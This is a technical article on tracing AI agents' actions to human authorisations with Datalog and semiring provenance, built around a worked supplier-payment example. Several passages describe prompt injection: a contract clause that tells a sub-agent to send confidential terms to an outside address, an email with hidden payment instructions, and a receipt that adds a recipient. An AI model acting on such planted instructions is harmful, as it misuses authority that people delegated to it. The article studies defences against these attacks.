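# Tracing an AI Agent's Actions to Human Authorizations with Semiring Provenance

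## Background: agents acting on permissions that people gave them

Semiring provenance is a technique for recording how the result of a query depends on the facts in a database. It labels each fact and carries the labels through every step of the query, so that the label on a result shows which facts support it and how they combine. The rules for combining labels come from a semiring, an algebraic structure with one operation for facts that are needed together and another for facts that are alternatives. Database researchers developed the technique for tables of data, but it applies to any conclusion that follows from recorded facts by fixed rules, such as "this program may make this payment."

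An AI agent is a program in which a language model chooses actions and carries them out through tools. Agents send email, change files and move money on permissions that people gave them, and someone may later need to know whose permission a particular action relied on. In *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, Booth, Fisher and colleagues (2026) asked industry, on behalf of the US National Institute of Standards and Technology, how an organisation can ensure the "binding back to human authorization" of what its agents do.

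### From a request to an action

A tool is ordinary software, such as a database query or a payment service, with a description that the model can read. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (Surapani, Kakitapelli and colleagues, 2026) describes how a model uses tools in a repeating cycle. The program that hosts the model gives it a list of tools. The model writes a structured request to use one, with arguments such as a payee and an amount. The host runs the request and adds the output to the model's context, which is all the text the model receives when it chooses its next step. The context therefore mixes the user's instructions with any web pages, documents and emails the tools returned.

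The model only produces text, and other software turns that text into a payment. A model's decision to call a tool is therefore not an authorisation decision. As Surapani and colleagues put it, "the model proposes", and the surrounding system must still establish who is asking, check that a permission covers the request and record what happened.

A principal is a person, organisation or software process that can hold or give permissions. A grant is a recorded act by which one principal gives another permission to do something within stated limits. Delegation means passing on all or part of a permission received from someone else. *Rethinking Access Control for AI Agents* (Zhou and Zhang, 2026) distinguishes a grant from an approval, by which a user or reviewer confirms a particular sensitive operation. It also distinguishes a grant from the availability of a tool, since an agent's list of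 tools can include a payment service that nobody has allowed it to use. Real grants are often vaguer than the definition suggests. For example, a user who types "triage these tickets" has stated a goal, and the model works out which operations the goal requires.

An agent shows a payment service or mail server that it has permission by sending a credential, usually a secret key or a signed string, with each request. Many credentials work for anyone who holds them. An agent can also start sub-agents, which are model-driven processes that each take on part of the task, and these need credentials too. *Delegation Without Trust* (Dantuluri and Sundi, 2026) reports that developers commonly give the main agent one broad credential, which it passes unchanged to its sub-agents and tools. Dantuluri and Sundi ran a scripted scenario on LangGraph, a widely used framework for building agents, and inspected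 the code of two others, CrewAI and AutoGen. They found that none of the three limits by default what a sub-agent can do with the authority it receives. The Model Context Protocol, a standard for connecting models to tools, has authorisation rules that supply some of the missing controls, but none that narrow a permission at each hand-over.

Dantuluri and Sundi also simulated an environment with 8,100 possible actions. A hijacked sub-agent could reach all of them with the shared credential, and 1.5 on average with a credential limited to its subtask. The larger number follows from the setup, since the shared credential allows every action. Both researchers work for a company that sells agent-security software, so they have an interest in finding a large difference, though they cite independent work that found similar defaults in an overlapping set of frameworks.

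### What the log leaves out

If an agent pays a bill with a finance director's credential, the bank's log will probably show a payment by the finance director. South (2025) reports in *Identity Management for Agentic AI*, a white paper for the OpenID Foundation, that services often log an agent's call in the same form as the user's own. The credential's owner may also have had no part in the decision to pay. For example, if an IT department owns the account the agent uses, the bank's records won't show who decided that the agent should pay suppliers.

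*OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Jones, Nadalin and colleagues), an internet standard for trading one credential for another, distinguishes acting as a user from acting on a user's behalf. An agent that acts as a user, which the standard calls impersonation, has the user's rights within some limits, and the service cannot tell the agent from the user. An agent that acts on a user's behalf keeps its own identity, and its credential can name both the agent and the user.

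Even a log with both names can be insufficient, because two people may have given the same agent the same right. *Observability for Delegated Execution in Agentic AI Systems* (Mishra and Sharad, 2026) gives a short proof of this. If a log records the actor, action and resource for each event, and the causal links between events, but not the delegation in force, then an agent that held two delegations over the period could have produced the same log under at least two assignments of events to delegations. No analysis of the log alone can then recover the right assignment. (The paper's six-event example is flawed because it contrasts sorting the events by causal trace with sorting them by tool, and both give the same result for the events listed. Swapping the two delegations fixes the example, which the general proof does not need.) A session number cannot reliably replace the missing field,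 since a retry can open a new session under an old delegation and sub-agents open sessions of their own. The system has to record the delegation when the action happens.

### Confused deputies and prompt injection

A program can use a genuine permission for the wrong person. Hardy's *The Confused Deputy* tells the "nearly true story" of a compiler at Tymshare, a company that rented out computer time. The compiler had permission to write in its system directory, where it kept usage statistics. Users could name a file to receive debugging output, and one of them named the billing file, which was in the same directory. The operating system allowed the write because the compiler had permission, even though the user didn't, and debugging output replaced the company's billing information. Hardy traces the fault to the compiler's having authority from two sources, the user and its own licence, with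 no way to express which one a given write relied on. A program is a confused deputy when someone who lacks its authority tricks it into using that authority for them.

Language models make the trick easier. In a prompt injection, someone places text in material an agent reads, and the model follows it as an instruction. *DelegateGuard* (Tran-Truong, Vo and colleagues, 2026) describes a user who asks an agent to summarise a confidential contract. The agent passes the formatting to a sub-agent, and a malicious clause in the contract contains an instruction to send the restrictive covenants to an outside web address first. Across 45 attacked runs in five office workflows, two open models proposed the attacker's action 42 and 44 times. Software outside the model blocked all of these proposals because each exceeded the user's grant.

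This defence works when the attacker wants something outside the grant. But Tran-Truong and colleagues prove that a monitor that ignores the content and quantity of what passes through it cannot prevent a leak to a destination that is both authorised and visible to the attacker. Payments raise the same difficulty whenever the injected request names a payee the agent is already allowed to pay.

### A payment of 400 dollars

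Consider a company with two agents, A and S, and a supplier, V. Its records contain four entries:

- **a**: Alice, the finance director, lets agent A pay approved suppliers.
- **b**: Bob, a project lead, gives A the same right.
- **c**: Carol, the compliance officer, approves supplier V.
- **d**: A passes its right to sub-agent S.

S reads an email, m, that contains hidden instructions to pay V. S then pays V 400 dollars. The payment passes a permission check because V is an approved supplier and S has permission to pay approved suppliers.

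A fact is a single statement that the database stores, typically as one row of a table. Here, a, b, c and d are facts. A query is a question put to the database, such as whether S may pay V. A rule is an if-then statement that produces new conclusions from facts and earlier conclusions. The company needs only a few rules. If Alice or Bob grants an agent the right to pay approved suppliers, the agent holds that right. If an agent holds the right and passes it to a sub-agent, the sub-agent also holds it. If an agent holds the right and compliance has approved a supplier, the agent may pay that supplier.

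A derivation is a way of reaching a result from input facts by applying rules. The query about S and V has two derivations. In the first, a gives A the right, d passes it to S, and c makes V an approved supplier, so S may pay V. The second starts with b instead of a and is otherwise the same. Both use Carol's approval and A's hand-over, but each uses only one of the grants from Alice and Bob.

Treating the grants as alternatives is a policy choice. *VERA* (2026), a scheme for withdrawing delegations between agents, uses the same policy and keeps an agent active as long as one valid chain of delegations still reaches it. A company that wanted both signatures would write a different rule, and the query would then have a single derivation containing all four facts. Products differ in how many parties an action needs. *AuthorityLens* (Chen, Jing and colleagues, 2026) identifies the smallest groups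 of principals that can bring about each of 599 operations. When OpenAI's coding agent Codex was set to ask for approval, 279 of the 597 achievable operations needed the user as well as the agent. With full access, the agent could bring about all 599 alone.

### Two questions about the payment

The derivations show that Alice's grant or Bob's, together with Carol's approval and A's delegation, permitted the payment. This is permission provenance, which traces the conclusion that the policy allows an action back to grants.

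What led the model to make the payment is a question about influence, meaning the effect of an item in the context on which action the model chose. The email m is the obvious candidate, but the fact that S paid after reading it does not establish that S paid because of it. An overdue invoice from V could have been in the same context and led to the same payment.

The answers can change independently. If we delete m, S still has permission to pay V but might no longer do so. If we withdraw a and b but keep m, the model may well request a payment that it has no right to make. Bob's grant can support the payment without any of its text entering the model's context. Conversely, Zhou and Zhang point out that documents and search results can "influence decisions without granting authority". Surapani and colleagues therefore keep two graphs, one for who passed authority to whom and one for where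 content came from and where it can flow. An inbox belongs in both because the agent needs permission to read it and it contains text from outsiders, which is how injected instructions get in. Mishra and Sharad accept that, for record-keeping, an action caused by injected text therefore still counts as an action under the delegation in force.

A policy can make permission depend partly on influence. If the company forbade payments prompted by an outside email, its judgment of whether a payment was permitted would be only as reliable as its method for detecting that influence.

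The word "provenance" causes some confusion here because writers on agent security mostly use it for the origin of content, which bears on what influenced an agent. *ResidualAuth* (Choi, Jeong and colleagues, 2026) uses "grant provenance" for the structure of who granted what to whom, which is closer to the database sense.

### Three separate literatures

The algebra of labels comes from database theory, the rules for passing on and withdrawing permissions come from computer security, and the methods for measuring influence come from research on language models. A search of work published up to early December 2026 found no system that combines all three, though several combine two or come close. Even the concept paper by Booth and colleagues lists access delegation and data-flow tracking as separate areas of interest.

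Work on agents has so far used semirings to label data. *Data Flow Control* (2026) applies them to the rows that agents' database queries return, and *PAGR* (2026) to the facts that a language model retrieves before it answers. For delegation, *Overlaying Governance* (2026) contains a theorem that, if the access rules are well formed, every action its scheme allows an agent has a human permission and a valid delegation chain behind it. The theorem guarantees only that at least one such chain exists. For the payment to V, Alice's chain alone would satisfy the theorem, so an auditor would still not know about Bob's.

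Other systems check both authorisation and the origin of content. *PACE* (2026) checks for paths by which protected data or an attacker's text could reach an action, and separately checks whether the action's effects are authorised. *AGATE* (2026) links each action to the origins of its authorisation and of the material it carries. In *Aligning Provenance with Authorization* (2026), a planning model that sees only the user's request and the list of tools writes down the permitted calls, and the system compares the agent's actions with that plan. All three infer influence from possible paths, matching text or another model's judgement. They do not measure how the model's choice would have changed without the email. *Kairos* (2026) lists a related task, following individual values through a language model's inference, as an open problem.

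*Authorization Revocation for Long-Running AI Agents* (Zhu and Wang, 2026) comes closest to permission provenance. For each permission in force, its protocol stores every minimal set of original grants sufficient to support it, and marks the set in use. If Carol's approval counts as an original grant, the entry for S would hold two sets, Alice with Carol and Bob with Carol, one of them marked. Zhu and Wang designed the record for revoking one person's authority without stopping work that someone else has independently authorised, and it does not include the email.

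## Writing grants and delegation as logical rules

Before software can check whether S may pay V, someone has to write the company's grants as facts and its policy as rules in a language the software can evaluate.

### The payment as a query

Datalog is a language for writing facts and rules of this kind. A fact names a relation and the things that stand in it. The company's four entries become:

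```
grants(alice, agent_a).          % a
grants(bob, agent_a).            % b
approves(carol, supplier_v).     % c
delegates(agent_a, agent_s).     % d
```

In a rule, a capital letter is a variable, the symbol `:-` means "if" and a comma means "and". The company's policy needs four rules:

```
holds(X)      :- grants(alice, X).                  % rule 1
holds(X)      :- grants(bob, X).                    % rule 2
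holds(Y)      :- holds(X), delegates(X, Y).         % rule 3
may_pay(X, V) :- holds(X), approves(carol, V).      % rule 4
```

Here `holds(X)` means that X has the right to pay approved suppliers. Rule 1 and fact a give `holds(agent_a)`. Rule 3 and fact d then give `holds(agent_s)`, and rule 4 and fact c give `may_pay(agent_s, supplier_v)`, or "S may pay V". The second derivation starts from b and rule 2 instead. A policy that required both signatures would replace rules 1 and 2 with `holds(X) :- grants(alice, X), grants(bob, X).`

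When no derivation exists, the service refuses the request. *Binder, a Logic-Based Security Language* (DeTreville, 2002) builds an access-control language on Datalog and treats a derivation as a proof that the service should grant access. A program can decide in polynomial time whether a Datalog conclusion follows. Datalog is also monotone, meaning that adding facts never removes a conclusion, so nobody can gain rights by withholding a document from the service. For the same reason, adding a fact that Alice has withdrawn her grant would have no effect, so DeTreville handles withdrawal in other ways, such as statements that expire. Prohibitions also need an extension to Datalog, and rule 3, which uses `holds` to define `holds`, needs extra care once conclusions carry labels.

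### Recording who made each statement

With these rules, anyone who can write to the company's database can forge a grant from Alice. A service that receives grants from elsewhere needs evidence of who made each one. *A Calculus for Access Control in Distributed Systems* (Abadi, Burrows and colleagues, 1993) defines a logic whose central formula is "A says s", where A is a principal and s is a statement or a command. A cryptographic key K can also be a principal, and "K says s" holds when K decrypts a message containing s. "A controls s" is short for "if A says s, then s", and an access control list is a set of such entries.

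The calculus also has names for combinations of principals. A joint signature by Alice and Bob means that each of them makes the statement, though not necessarily together. "B for A" means B acting on A's behalf under a delegation. If agent A acts for Alice and starts sub-agent S, a request from S comes from "S for (A for Alice)", so the requester's name includes the delegation chain behind the request. A request that relied on Bob's grant would have a different name, so the name on a single request shows only one of the two chains.

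DeTreville brought "says" into Datalog. A service that receives a signed certificate stores its content as a statement by the signer, and a rule determines whether the service believes it:

```
alice says holds(agent_a).
holds(X) :- alice says holds(X).
holds(Y) :- holds(X), X says holds(Y).
```

In a real system, `alice` would stand for Alice's public key. The first line would have no effect without the second. A forged grant in the email m is therefore harmless, because m does not carry Alice's signature. However, if agent A has its own key, injected text could lead A to sign a delegation d to S. The signature on d would be genuine, and the query would treat d like any other fact.

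The contents of a derivation depend on who does the reasoning. In one of DeTreville's examples, a company's research lab certifies that John Smith works there, and the company counts all lab staff as its own employees. If a service collects these statements and concludes for itself that Smith is an employee, its derivation includes the lab's certificate. The company's personnel office can instead do the reasoning and send the service one certificate with the conclusion. The decision is the same, but the lab is missing from the service's derivation. Similarly, if the finance department's software checked Alice's grant and signed a new certificate for agent A, the payment service could trace the payment only to the finance department.

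### Certificates, SecPAL and proofs from the requester

Clarke, Elien and colleagues, in *Certificate chain discovery in SPKI/SDSI*, describe SPKI/SDSI as a certificate system that emphasises naming, groups and flexible authorisation. One type of certificate defines a name, such as "faculty of this university". The other passes on a permission and has five parts: the issuer's key, the subject, a mark that shows whether the subject may delegate further, the permission itself and a validity period. A service grants access if certificates lead from the resource's owner to the requester. Some policies don't fit this format. For example, DeTreville points out that SDSI's mechanism for defining groups cannot express the rule that an employee may read a file if the employee's boss approves. Carol's approval is the same kind of condition.

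SecPAL, which Becker, Fournet and Gordon presented in *Design and Semantics of a Decentralized Authorization Language* in 2007, is closer to ordinary English. In their example, a user wants a computing cluster to analyse data on a file server. The server says that she can read a directory, and she says that the cluster can read one file in it until a certain date. The server's policy lets anyone who can read a directory pass on the right to read a file in it, unless the file is confidential. After checking that the date hasn't passed and the file isn't confidential, the server derives from these two statements that the cluster can read the file.

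SecPAL writes delegation as "can say", with a subscript that shows whether the recipient may delegate further. If the company's policy let Alice say who can pay suppliers but not re-delegate that power, any derivation from her statement would depend only on statements she had issued. Becker and colleagues prove this and point out that two earlier languages with limits on delegation did not guarantee it.

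In proof-carrying authorisation, the requester, rather than the service, searches for a derivation. *Proof-carrying authentication* (Appel and Felten, 1999) uses higher-order logic, which is much more expressive than Datalog. No procedure can decide every request in this logic, but checking a finished proof is simple, so users must send a proof with each request. *A General and Flexible Access-Control System for the Web* (Bauer, Schneider and Felten) applies the idea to websites and adds ways to find pieces of policy on different hosts. DeTreville lets requesters supply proofs as an option, to reduce the work of a busy service.

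If the service keeps the proof, it has a record of which statements justified the action, but the requester chose that proof. S could always send the derivation that starts with Alice's grant, and the service would not need to look for Bob's. An auditor who read the stored proofs would then underestimate how many people's grants permitted the payment.

A proof may also omit who wrote the rules. *Commune* (Soriente, Karame and colleagues, 2013) considers files with several owners, where a user needs signed permission from a minimum number of them. A Datalog program can enforce this, but its administrator can rewrite the rules to let in people who lack the signatures. *Commune* avoids the problem by spreading each file over the owners' own accounts. A company with a central rule set could instead sign and label the rules as well as the grants, so that each derivation also shows who set the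 policy.

### Earlier attempts to trace authorisations

In the logics above, a conclusion does not show how the service reached it. *A Logic for Authorization Provenance* (Hu, Zhang and colleagues, 2010) gives the example of a building whose door opens if the system can derive that Alice, the warden, believes it should. Alice may have said so herself, or she may have delegated the decision to Bob, who passed it on through Cathy and David to Emma, who said the door should open.

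Their logic distinguishes the two cases with an operator that means "due to agent i", where an agent is any principal. If Alice trusts Bob on a statement and Bob asserts it, then Alice believes it due to Bob. Suppose Alice holds that the door may open when the alarm is off, trusts Bob to check the alarm, and hears from Bob that it is off. Her belief that the door should open is then due to Alice and Bob together. The building's owners can use the operator to restrict who decides. If the management board consists of Alice, Bob, Cathy and David, the owners can require a proof that the decision to open the door is due to board members only. The longer chain cannot meet this requirement because it depends on Emma's word and she is not on the board, so the door stays shut.

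The operator is better suited to this kind of check than to attribution. One of the logic's axioms lets anyone enlarge the set of agents, so a conclusion that is due to Alice and Bob is also due to Alice, Bob and Emma, even if Emma did nothing. For the payment, the logic would support one statement with Alice, Carol and agent A in the set, another with Bob in place of Alice, and a third with all four. An auditor would have to search for the smallest sets to learn that Alice's grant and Bob's are alternatives.

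A 2012 follow-up by Hu, Khan and colleagues, *Tracking and Constraining Authorization Provenance*, applies the logic to fraud. A company requires two different treasurers to prepare and approve each cheque, but lets a treasurer delegate to a clerk. One treasurer delegates the preparation to a clerk, who makes out a cheque to the treasurer, and the treasurer approves it. Two people took part, but the authority for both steps came from the same treasurer. Hu and colleagues prevent this by keeping a history of past authorisations and refusing combinations in which both steps trace back to one person. They note that a user could also get around the requirement by creating dummy agents, such as extra processes. This is easy with AI agents, since one person's agent can start any number of sub-agents. A rule that required only two different agents would accept agent A and sub-agent S even if both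 acted on Alice's grant.

Hu and colleagues doubt that database provenance carries over to authorisation, because database provenance concerns data and how a system processed it, while authorisation provenance concerns the agents responsible. The difference is smaller when the data are signed grants, because each grant names the agent who issued it.

Webdamlog, a Datalog-style language for sharing data between people's devices and accounts, uses database provenance to control access. *Introducing Access Control in Webdamlog* (Abiteboul, Antoine and colleagues, 2013) gives an example of a fact that can be derived either from one stored fact or from two others together. By default, a user who can read the collection that holds the derived fact can read the fact itself only if they can also read the first stored fact or both of the others. The rule distinguishes alternative from joint use, but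 it traces only the data, not the permission to read it. The default can be too strict. If Alice publishes photos to everyone on her friends list, her friend Pete cannot see them unless he can also read the list, so the language lets Alice hide the list from the provenance.

Webdamlog also lets one user install a rule on another's machine. If Bob's rule ran on Alice's machine with her privileges, he could use it to send hate mail from her account or copy her secret files. Abiteboul and colleagues instead run the rule with Bob's privileges and mark its effects as his. This avoids the confusion between two sources of authority that occurred in Hardy's compiler.

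Semirings came into authorisation through SPKI/SDSI. Early search methods looked for one chain of certificates that covered the whole request, so a user's request to read and write a directory failed if one certificate allowed reading and another allowed writing. *On generalized authorization problems* (Schwoon, Jha and colleagues, 2003) introduced a framework that allows several chains, and *Weighted Pushdown Systems and Trust-Management Systems* (Jha, Schwoon and colleagues) extended it to certificates on different servers. Each certificate is labelled with the permission it gives. Along a chain, the algorithm takes the intersection of the labels, since a chain passes on only what every certificate in it allows. Across chains it takes the union, so the two certificates together permit reading and writing. Sets of permissions with these two operations form a semiring. Other labels in the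 same framework handle recency, validity, privacy and trust.

These labels show what a principal may do but not whose grants allow it. In the payment example, Alice's chain and Bob's would both have the label "pay". Their union is also "pay", which would be the result even if Bob had granted nothing. Jha and colleagues also produce a graph of certificates as evidence for the final label, but a graph with only Alice's chain would meet their definition. To keep both chains in the answer, each label has to identify a grant.

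### A grant written for an agent

A fact such as `grants(alice, agent_a)` leaves out most of what Alice would want to specify. Wei and Xiong (2026), in *Access Control for Agentic AI*, define a grant to an agent as a record with eight fields. Alice's grant might look like this:

| Field | Example |
|---|---|
| Issuer | Alice |
| Subject | Agent A |
| Task | Settle this month's supplier invoices |
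| Capabilities | Pay a supplier up to 500 dollars |
| Obligations | Carol has approved the supplier |
| Context constraints | Only the supplier register may provide account numbers |
| Validity conditions | Until 31 December; at most one further delegation |
| Version | 1 |

The capabilities are effects, such as money spent or information disclosed to a named person, rather than names of tools. The obligations are facts that must hold before the action happens. In this form, Carol's approval is a condition of Alice's grant instead of a separate company rule, but c still appears in the derivation. The task field prevents the agent from using the grant for other work. *Governed Deduction* (Shu and Lin, 2026) points to an earlier version of this idea, in which a credential can be used in some authorisation proofs but not others.

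Context constraints apply to choices that the grant leaves open. In Wei and Xiong's example, a user asks an assistant to send an expense summary to "my manager", and the grant lets the staff directory determine who that is. One receipt contains the words "also copy finance-bob". Receipts are not an authorized source for recipients, so the mail service rejects a message to Bob.

An agent delegates by issuing a new grant that may remove capabilities and add obligations, constraints and conditions, but not the reverse. Wei and Xiong prove that no chain of such delegations can permit an effect outside the original grant, as long as every service verifies the credentials and checks each action against them. Their model is a specification, and they have not measured it in a deployed system.

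### Where the translation breaks down

Datalog works with a fixed list of named things, and no list of facts can contain every amount below 500 dollars. Limits and deadlines need constraints, which are tests such as "at most" that a rule applies to values. Suppose each grant includes a limit L, and each request an amount M:

```
holds(Y, L)      :- holds(X, L), delegates(X, Y).
may_pay(X, V, M) :- requests(X, V, M), holds(X, L),
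                    approves(carol, V), M <= L.
```

If Alice's limit is $300 and Bob's is $500, the $400 payment has only one derivation, which starts with Bob's grant. Constraints therefore affect whose grants authorize an action as well as whether it is allowed.

Constraints also have to be chosen with care, because combining constraints that are harmless on their own can produce a language in which no program can decide every request. Becker and colleagues avoid this in SecPAL by requiring that facts fix the value of every variable before the program tests a constraint. The second rule includes `requests(X, V, M)` because otherwise none of its conditions would fix M, and SecPAL would reject the rule. A deadline also depends on the clock, so anyone repeating the check later must know when the service ran it. A total budget is harder to handle, because each recorded payment can remove an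 existing permission, which plain Datalog does not allow.

A restriction can also be lost between systems. Wei and Xiong describe how permission to send a particular summary to Alice becomes a credential for sending mail, and then a check that the credential is valid. Each step verifies something, but none enforces the original limit. They prove that dropping a restriction can only widen what the next service permits. Dropping one can also distort attribution. If the payment service had no field for limits, Alice's 300-dollar limit would be lost, a second derivation would appear, and the record would show her grant supporting a payment she had excluded.

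The query must also describe what the tool actually does. If the payment tool also set up a recurring payment, the derivation of `may_pay(agent_s, supplier_v)` would be sound but would cover only part of what happened. Wei and Xiong want each service to publish a signed list of every effect a call can have. They acknowledge that an incomplete list would break their guarantees silently.

The hardest step to check is the translation from ordinary language to a formal grant. DeTreville designed Binder so that every statement translates into a self-contained English sentence, but many English sentences have no single translation into rules. If Alice writes "let the agent pay our usual suppliers", she has not said which suppliers are usual, how much the agent may spend or whether it may use sub-agents. Whoever drafts the formal grant has to decide. Rule 3, for instance, lets sub-agents inherit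 the right whether or not Alice thought about them. When a language model drafts the grant, fact a records the model's interpretation of Alice's words, and a derivation traces back only as far as a. Asking Alice to confirm the draft helps only if she understands it. Keeping her original sentence with the formal grant would at least let an auditor compare the two, though the auditor would have to judge whether they match, since no query can settle that.

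## Why-provenance and how-provenance of a permission

Database provenance gives each fact its own label, or token, instead of a shared label such as "pay". In the payment example, a and b label the grants from Alice and Bob, c labels Carol's approval of supplier V, and d labels agent A's delegation to sub-agent S. Database researchers have defined several kinds of provenance, which preserve different amounts of detail about how a result such as `may_pay(agent_s, supplier_v)` follows from the facts.

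### Lineage and witnesses

Lineage is the single set of all inputs that contributed to a result in any derivation. For the payment to V, it is {a, b, c, d}. Cheney, Chiticariu and Tan (2009), in *Provenance in Databases*, credit Cui and colleagues with one of the first formal definitions. Lineage can greatly narrow an investigation, since a company might have thousands of grants on file and only these four facts bear on the payment. But it does not show how the four facts combine. If the company required signatures from both Alice and Bob, the lineage would still be {a, b, c, d}, even though withdrawing either grant would then block the payment.

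A witness is a set of facts that is enough to produce a result. Both {a, c, d} and {b, c, d} are witnesses for the payment. So is {a, b, c, d}, because Datalog is monotone, meaning an extra fact never removes a conclusion. If the database also held ten grants unrelated to S or V, each of these three witnesses could include any subset of them, and the payment would have 3 × 2¹⁰ = 3,072 witnesses.

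Why-provenance, which Buneman and colleagues introduced in 2001, keeps only the witnesses that the query's derivations use. Each derivation contributes the set of facts it starts from, so the why-provenance of the payment is {{a, c, d}, {b, c, d}}. Cheney and colleagues prove that every witness contains at least one of these sets. To tell whether a collection of grants would permit the payment, an auditor therefore only needs to check whether it includes Alice's set or Bob's.

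A witness is minimal if none of its proper subsets is also a witness. Here {a, c, d} and {b, c, d} are both minimal, so the why-provenance is the same as the set of minimal witnesses, though the two can differ. For each permission, Zhu and Wang's revocation protocol stores sets of original grants, which are minimal witnesses.

Glavic (2021), in *Data Provenance*, calls a fact necessary if every witness contains it. For a monotone query, a fact is necessary exactly when removing it alone would remove the result. In the payment example, the necessary facts are Carol's approval (c) and A's delegation (d). If we remove either Alice's grant or Bob's, the other still permits the payment, so an auditor who tested the grants one by one would wrongly conclude that neither mattered. But c and d could not permit the payment on their own, because nobody would have given A the right to pay. Listing the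 witnesses avoids this mistake because it keeps the alternatives in separate sets.

The names of these concepts vary between papers. *Provenance Semirings* (Green, Karvounarakis and Tannen, 2007) uses "why-provenance" for the set of all contributing inputs, which Cheney and colleagues call "lineage". *The Semiring Framework for Database Provenance*, a conference talk (Tannen, 2017), lists three meanings of "lineage": a set of contributing facts, a collection of minimal witnesses, and a collection of witnesses that also counts repeated derivations.

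### Deriving the polynomial

How-provenance records every derivation and how many times each one uses each input. It is a polynomial whose variables are the tokens. Green and colleagues developed it after noticing very similar arithmetic in four existing ways of computing with labelled tables, which recorded uncertain facts, probabilities, duplicate rows and lineage.

The structure common to all of them is a commutative semiring. This is a set of labels with an addition for alternatives, a multiplication for joint use and two special labels, 0 and 1, that obey the following laws for all labels x, y and z:

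- x + y = y + x, and x · y = y · x
- (x + y) + z = x + (y + z), and (x · y) · z = x · (y · z)
- x + 0 = x, and x · 1 = x
- x · 0 = 0
- x · (y + z) = x · y + x · z

A semiring doesn't need subtraction or division. The label 0 marks an absent fact, and the label 1 can mark a fact that is present but that nobody wants to track.

Green and colleagues define how labels pass through the basic operations on tables:

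| Operation | Effect on the table | Label of each row in the result |
|---|---|---|
| Union | Merges two tables with the same columns | Sum of the row's labels in the two tables |
| Projection | Drops columns, which can make different rows identical | Sum of the labels of the rows that became identical |
| Selection | Keeps the rows that pass a test | The row's label times 1 if it passes, or times 0 if it fails |
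| Join | Combines rows from two tables that agree on their shared columns | Product of the two rows' labels |

Each of the company's Datalog rules combines these operations. The `grants` table has one row for Alice's grant to agent A, labelled a, and one for Bob's, labelled b. Rule 1 selects the grants from Alice, which leaves a · 1 = a for her row and b · 0 = 0 for Bob's. It then drops the column that names the grantor, so `holds(agent_a)` gets the label a + 0 = a. Rule 2 does the same for Bob and gives b. Both rules derive `holds(agent_a)`, so the union of their results has the label a + b.

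Rule 3 joins `holds` with `delegates`. The row for agent A has the label a + b and the delegation to S has the label d, so `holds(agent_s)` gets (a + b) · d. Rule 4 joins this with Carol's approval:

```
may_pay(agent_s, supplier_v):  (a + b) · d · c  =  acd + bcd
```

The polynomial acd + bcd has one term for each derivation, and each term is the product of the facts that the derivation uses. If the company required both signatures, the polynomial would be the single term abcd. Rule 3 uses `holds` to define `holds`, but the calculation stops after one step because the company has only one delegation. If agents delegated in a loop, there could be infinitely many derivations, and an ordinary polynomial could not have a term for each.

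Tannen says that tracking only the joint use of facts is "basically like keeping a log", and that tracking alternatives is also essential. A log of Alice's derivation would contain a, c and d but would not show that Bob's grant was an alternative.

Access control depends on the law x · 0 = 0, where 0 is the label for an absent fact. To compute lineage, Green and colleagues used set union for both addition and multiplication, and the empty set for both 0 and 1, which breaks this law. If Carol had never approved V, her missing approval would have the empty set as its label. The join in rule 4 would then produce {a, b, d}, which is not the label for an absent fact, so the payment would appear to be permitted. Cheney and colleagues avoid this by giving absent facts a separate "undefined" label, and joining anything with that label gives an undefined result.

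### Why the labels have to form a semiring

Database software routinely rewrites queries to run faster. It could combine Alice's and Bob's grants and then apply A's delegation, which gives (a + b) · d, or apply the delegation to each grant and then combine the results, which gives ad + bd. An auditor would want a payment's provenance to be the same under either plan, and the distributive law ensures this by making the two expressions equal.

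Green and colleagues prove a general version of this. They list the identities that people expect of queries:

- Union is associative and commutative, and a union with an empty table changes nothing.
- Join is associative and commutative, and it distributes over union.
- Projections and selections can trade places with each other and with unions and joins, wherever the columns allow it.
- A selection that every row passes changes nothing, and one that every row fails leaves an empty table.

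All of these identities hold for labelled tables if and only if the labels form a commutative semiring. If a company's labelling scheme breaks one of the semiring laws, some pair of interchangeable queries will give the same fact different labels.

This mistake is easy to make with probabilities. Suppose the security team estimates the probability that each grant is genuine as 0.6 for a, 0.5 for b and 0.7 for d, and treats these as independent. It might multiply the probabilities of facts used together, and combine two alternatives x and y with the formula for independent events, x + y − xy. If the software combines a and b first, the result is 0.8, and multiplying by 0.7 gives the correct answer, 0.56. If it applies the delegation first, the two chains have probabilities of 0.42 and 0.35, and the formula gives 0.623. This is wrong because the chains are not independent, since both fail if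 d is a forgery. The figures come from an example that Cheney and colleagues give for Trio, a database system for uncertain data. Trio stores a formula made of tokens and calculates the probability from it, so it can account for a shared token.

### One polynomial, several evaluations

To evaluate a polynomial, we replace each token with a value from some semiring and use that semiring's addition and multiplication. Green and colleagues prove that this gives the same answer as replacing the tokens first and then running the query. In symbols, let R be the input table with its values, let R̄ be the same table with a separate token on each row, and let v be the function that assigns a value to each token. Then for any query q built from the operations above,

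```
q(R) = Eval_v( q(R̄) )
```

The theorem holds because evaluation is a homomorphism, meaning that it preserves sums, products, 0 and 1. A query changes labels using only these operations and constants, so replacing the tokens with values before the query gives the same result as replacing them afterwards. Conversely, if a function on labels is not a homomorphism, some query will give different results depending on whether the function is applied before or after it. In an example from Green and colleagues, a row in the result has the polynomial 2r² + rs. If the input contains five copies of the row labelled r and one copy of the row labelled s, the polynomial gives 2 × 25 + 5 = 55, which is the number of copies a database that keeps duplicates would return.

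For the company, this means that it can run the permission query once, store acd + bcd, and answer different questions from it later. Three of them are:

```
Is the payment allowed if Alice withdraws her grant?
   (false and true and true) or (true and true and true)  =  true

How many derivations does it have?
   1·1·1 + 1·1·1  =  2

How well has the company verified the grants behind it?
   max( min(3, 2, 3), min(1, 2, 3) )  =  max(2, 1)  =  2
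```

For the first question, the values are true and false, addition is "or", and multiplication is "and". Bob's grant still permits the payment. If Carol withdrew her approval instead, both terms would become false and S could no longer pay V.

The second question uses ordinary numbers, and its answer counts derivations rather than people. If A had recorded its delegation to S twice, d would be 2 and the total would be 4, but Alice and Bob would still be the only people who had granted the right.

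The third question uses assurance levels. Suppose the company assigns level 1 to a grant if someone only typed the issuer's name, level 2 if the issuer logged in with a password, and level 3 if the issuer signed with a hardware key. Alice's grant is at level 3, Bob's is at level 1, Carol's approval is at level 2, and the delegation is at level 3. A derivation is only as reliable as its weakest fact, so multiplication is the minimum. The permission is as reliable as its best derivation, so addition is the maximum. An absent fact has the value 0, and level 3, the highest level, is the semiring's multiplicative identity.

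The answer of 2 comes from Alice's derivation, and Carol's approval limits it. If Alice withdrew her grant, the level would fall to 1. A payment service that required level 2 would then refuse the payment, although the true-or-false query would still allow it. Assurance levels therefore show a dependence on Alice that the true-or-false answer doesn't show.

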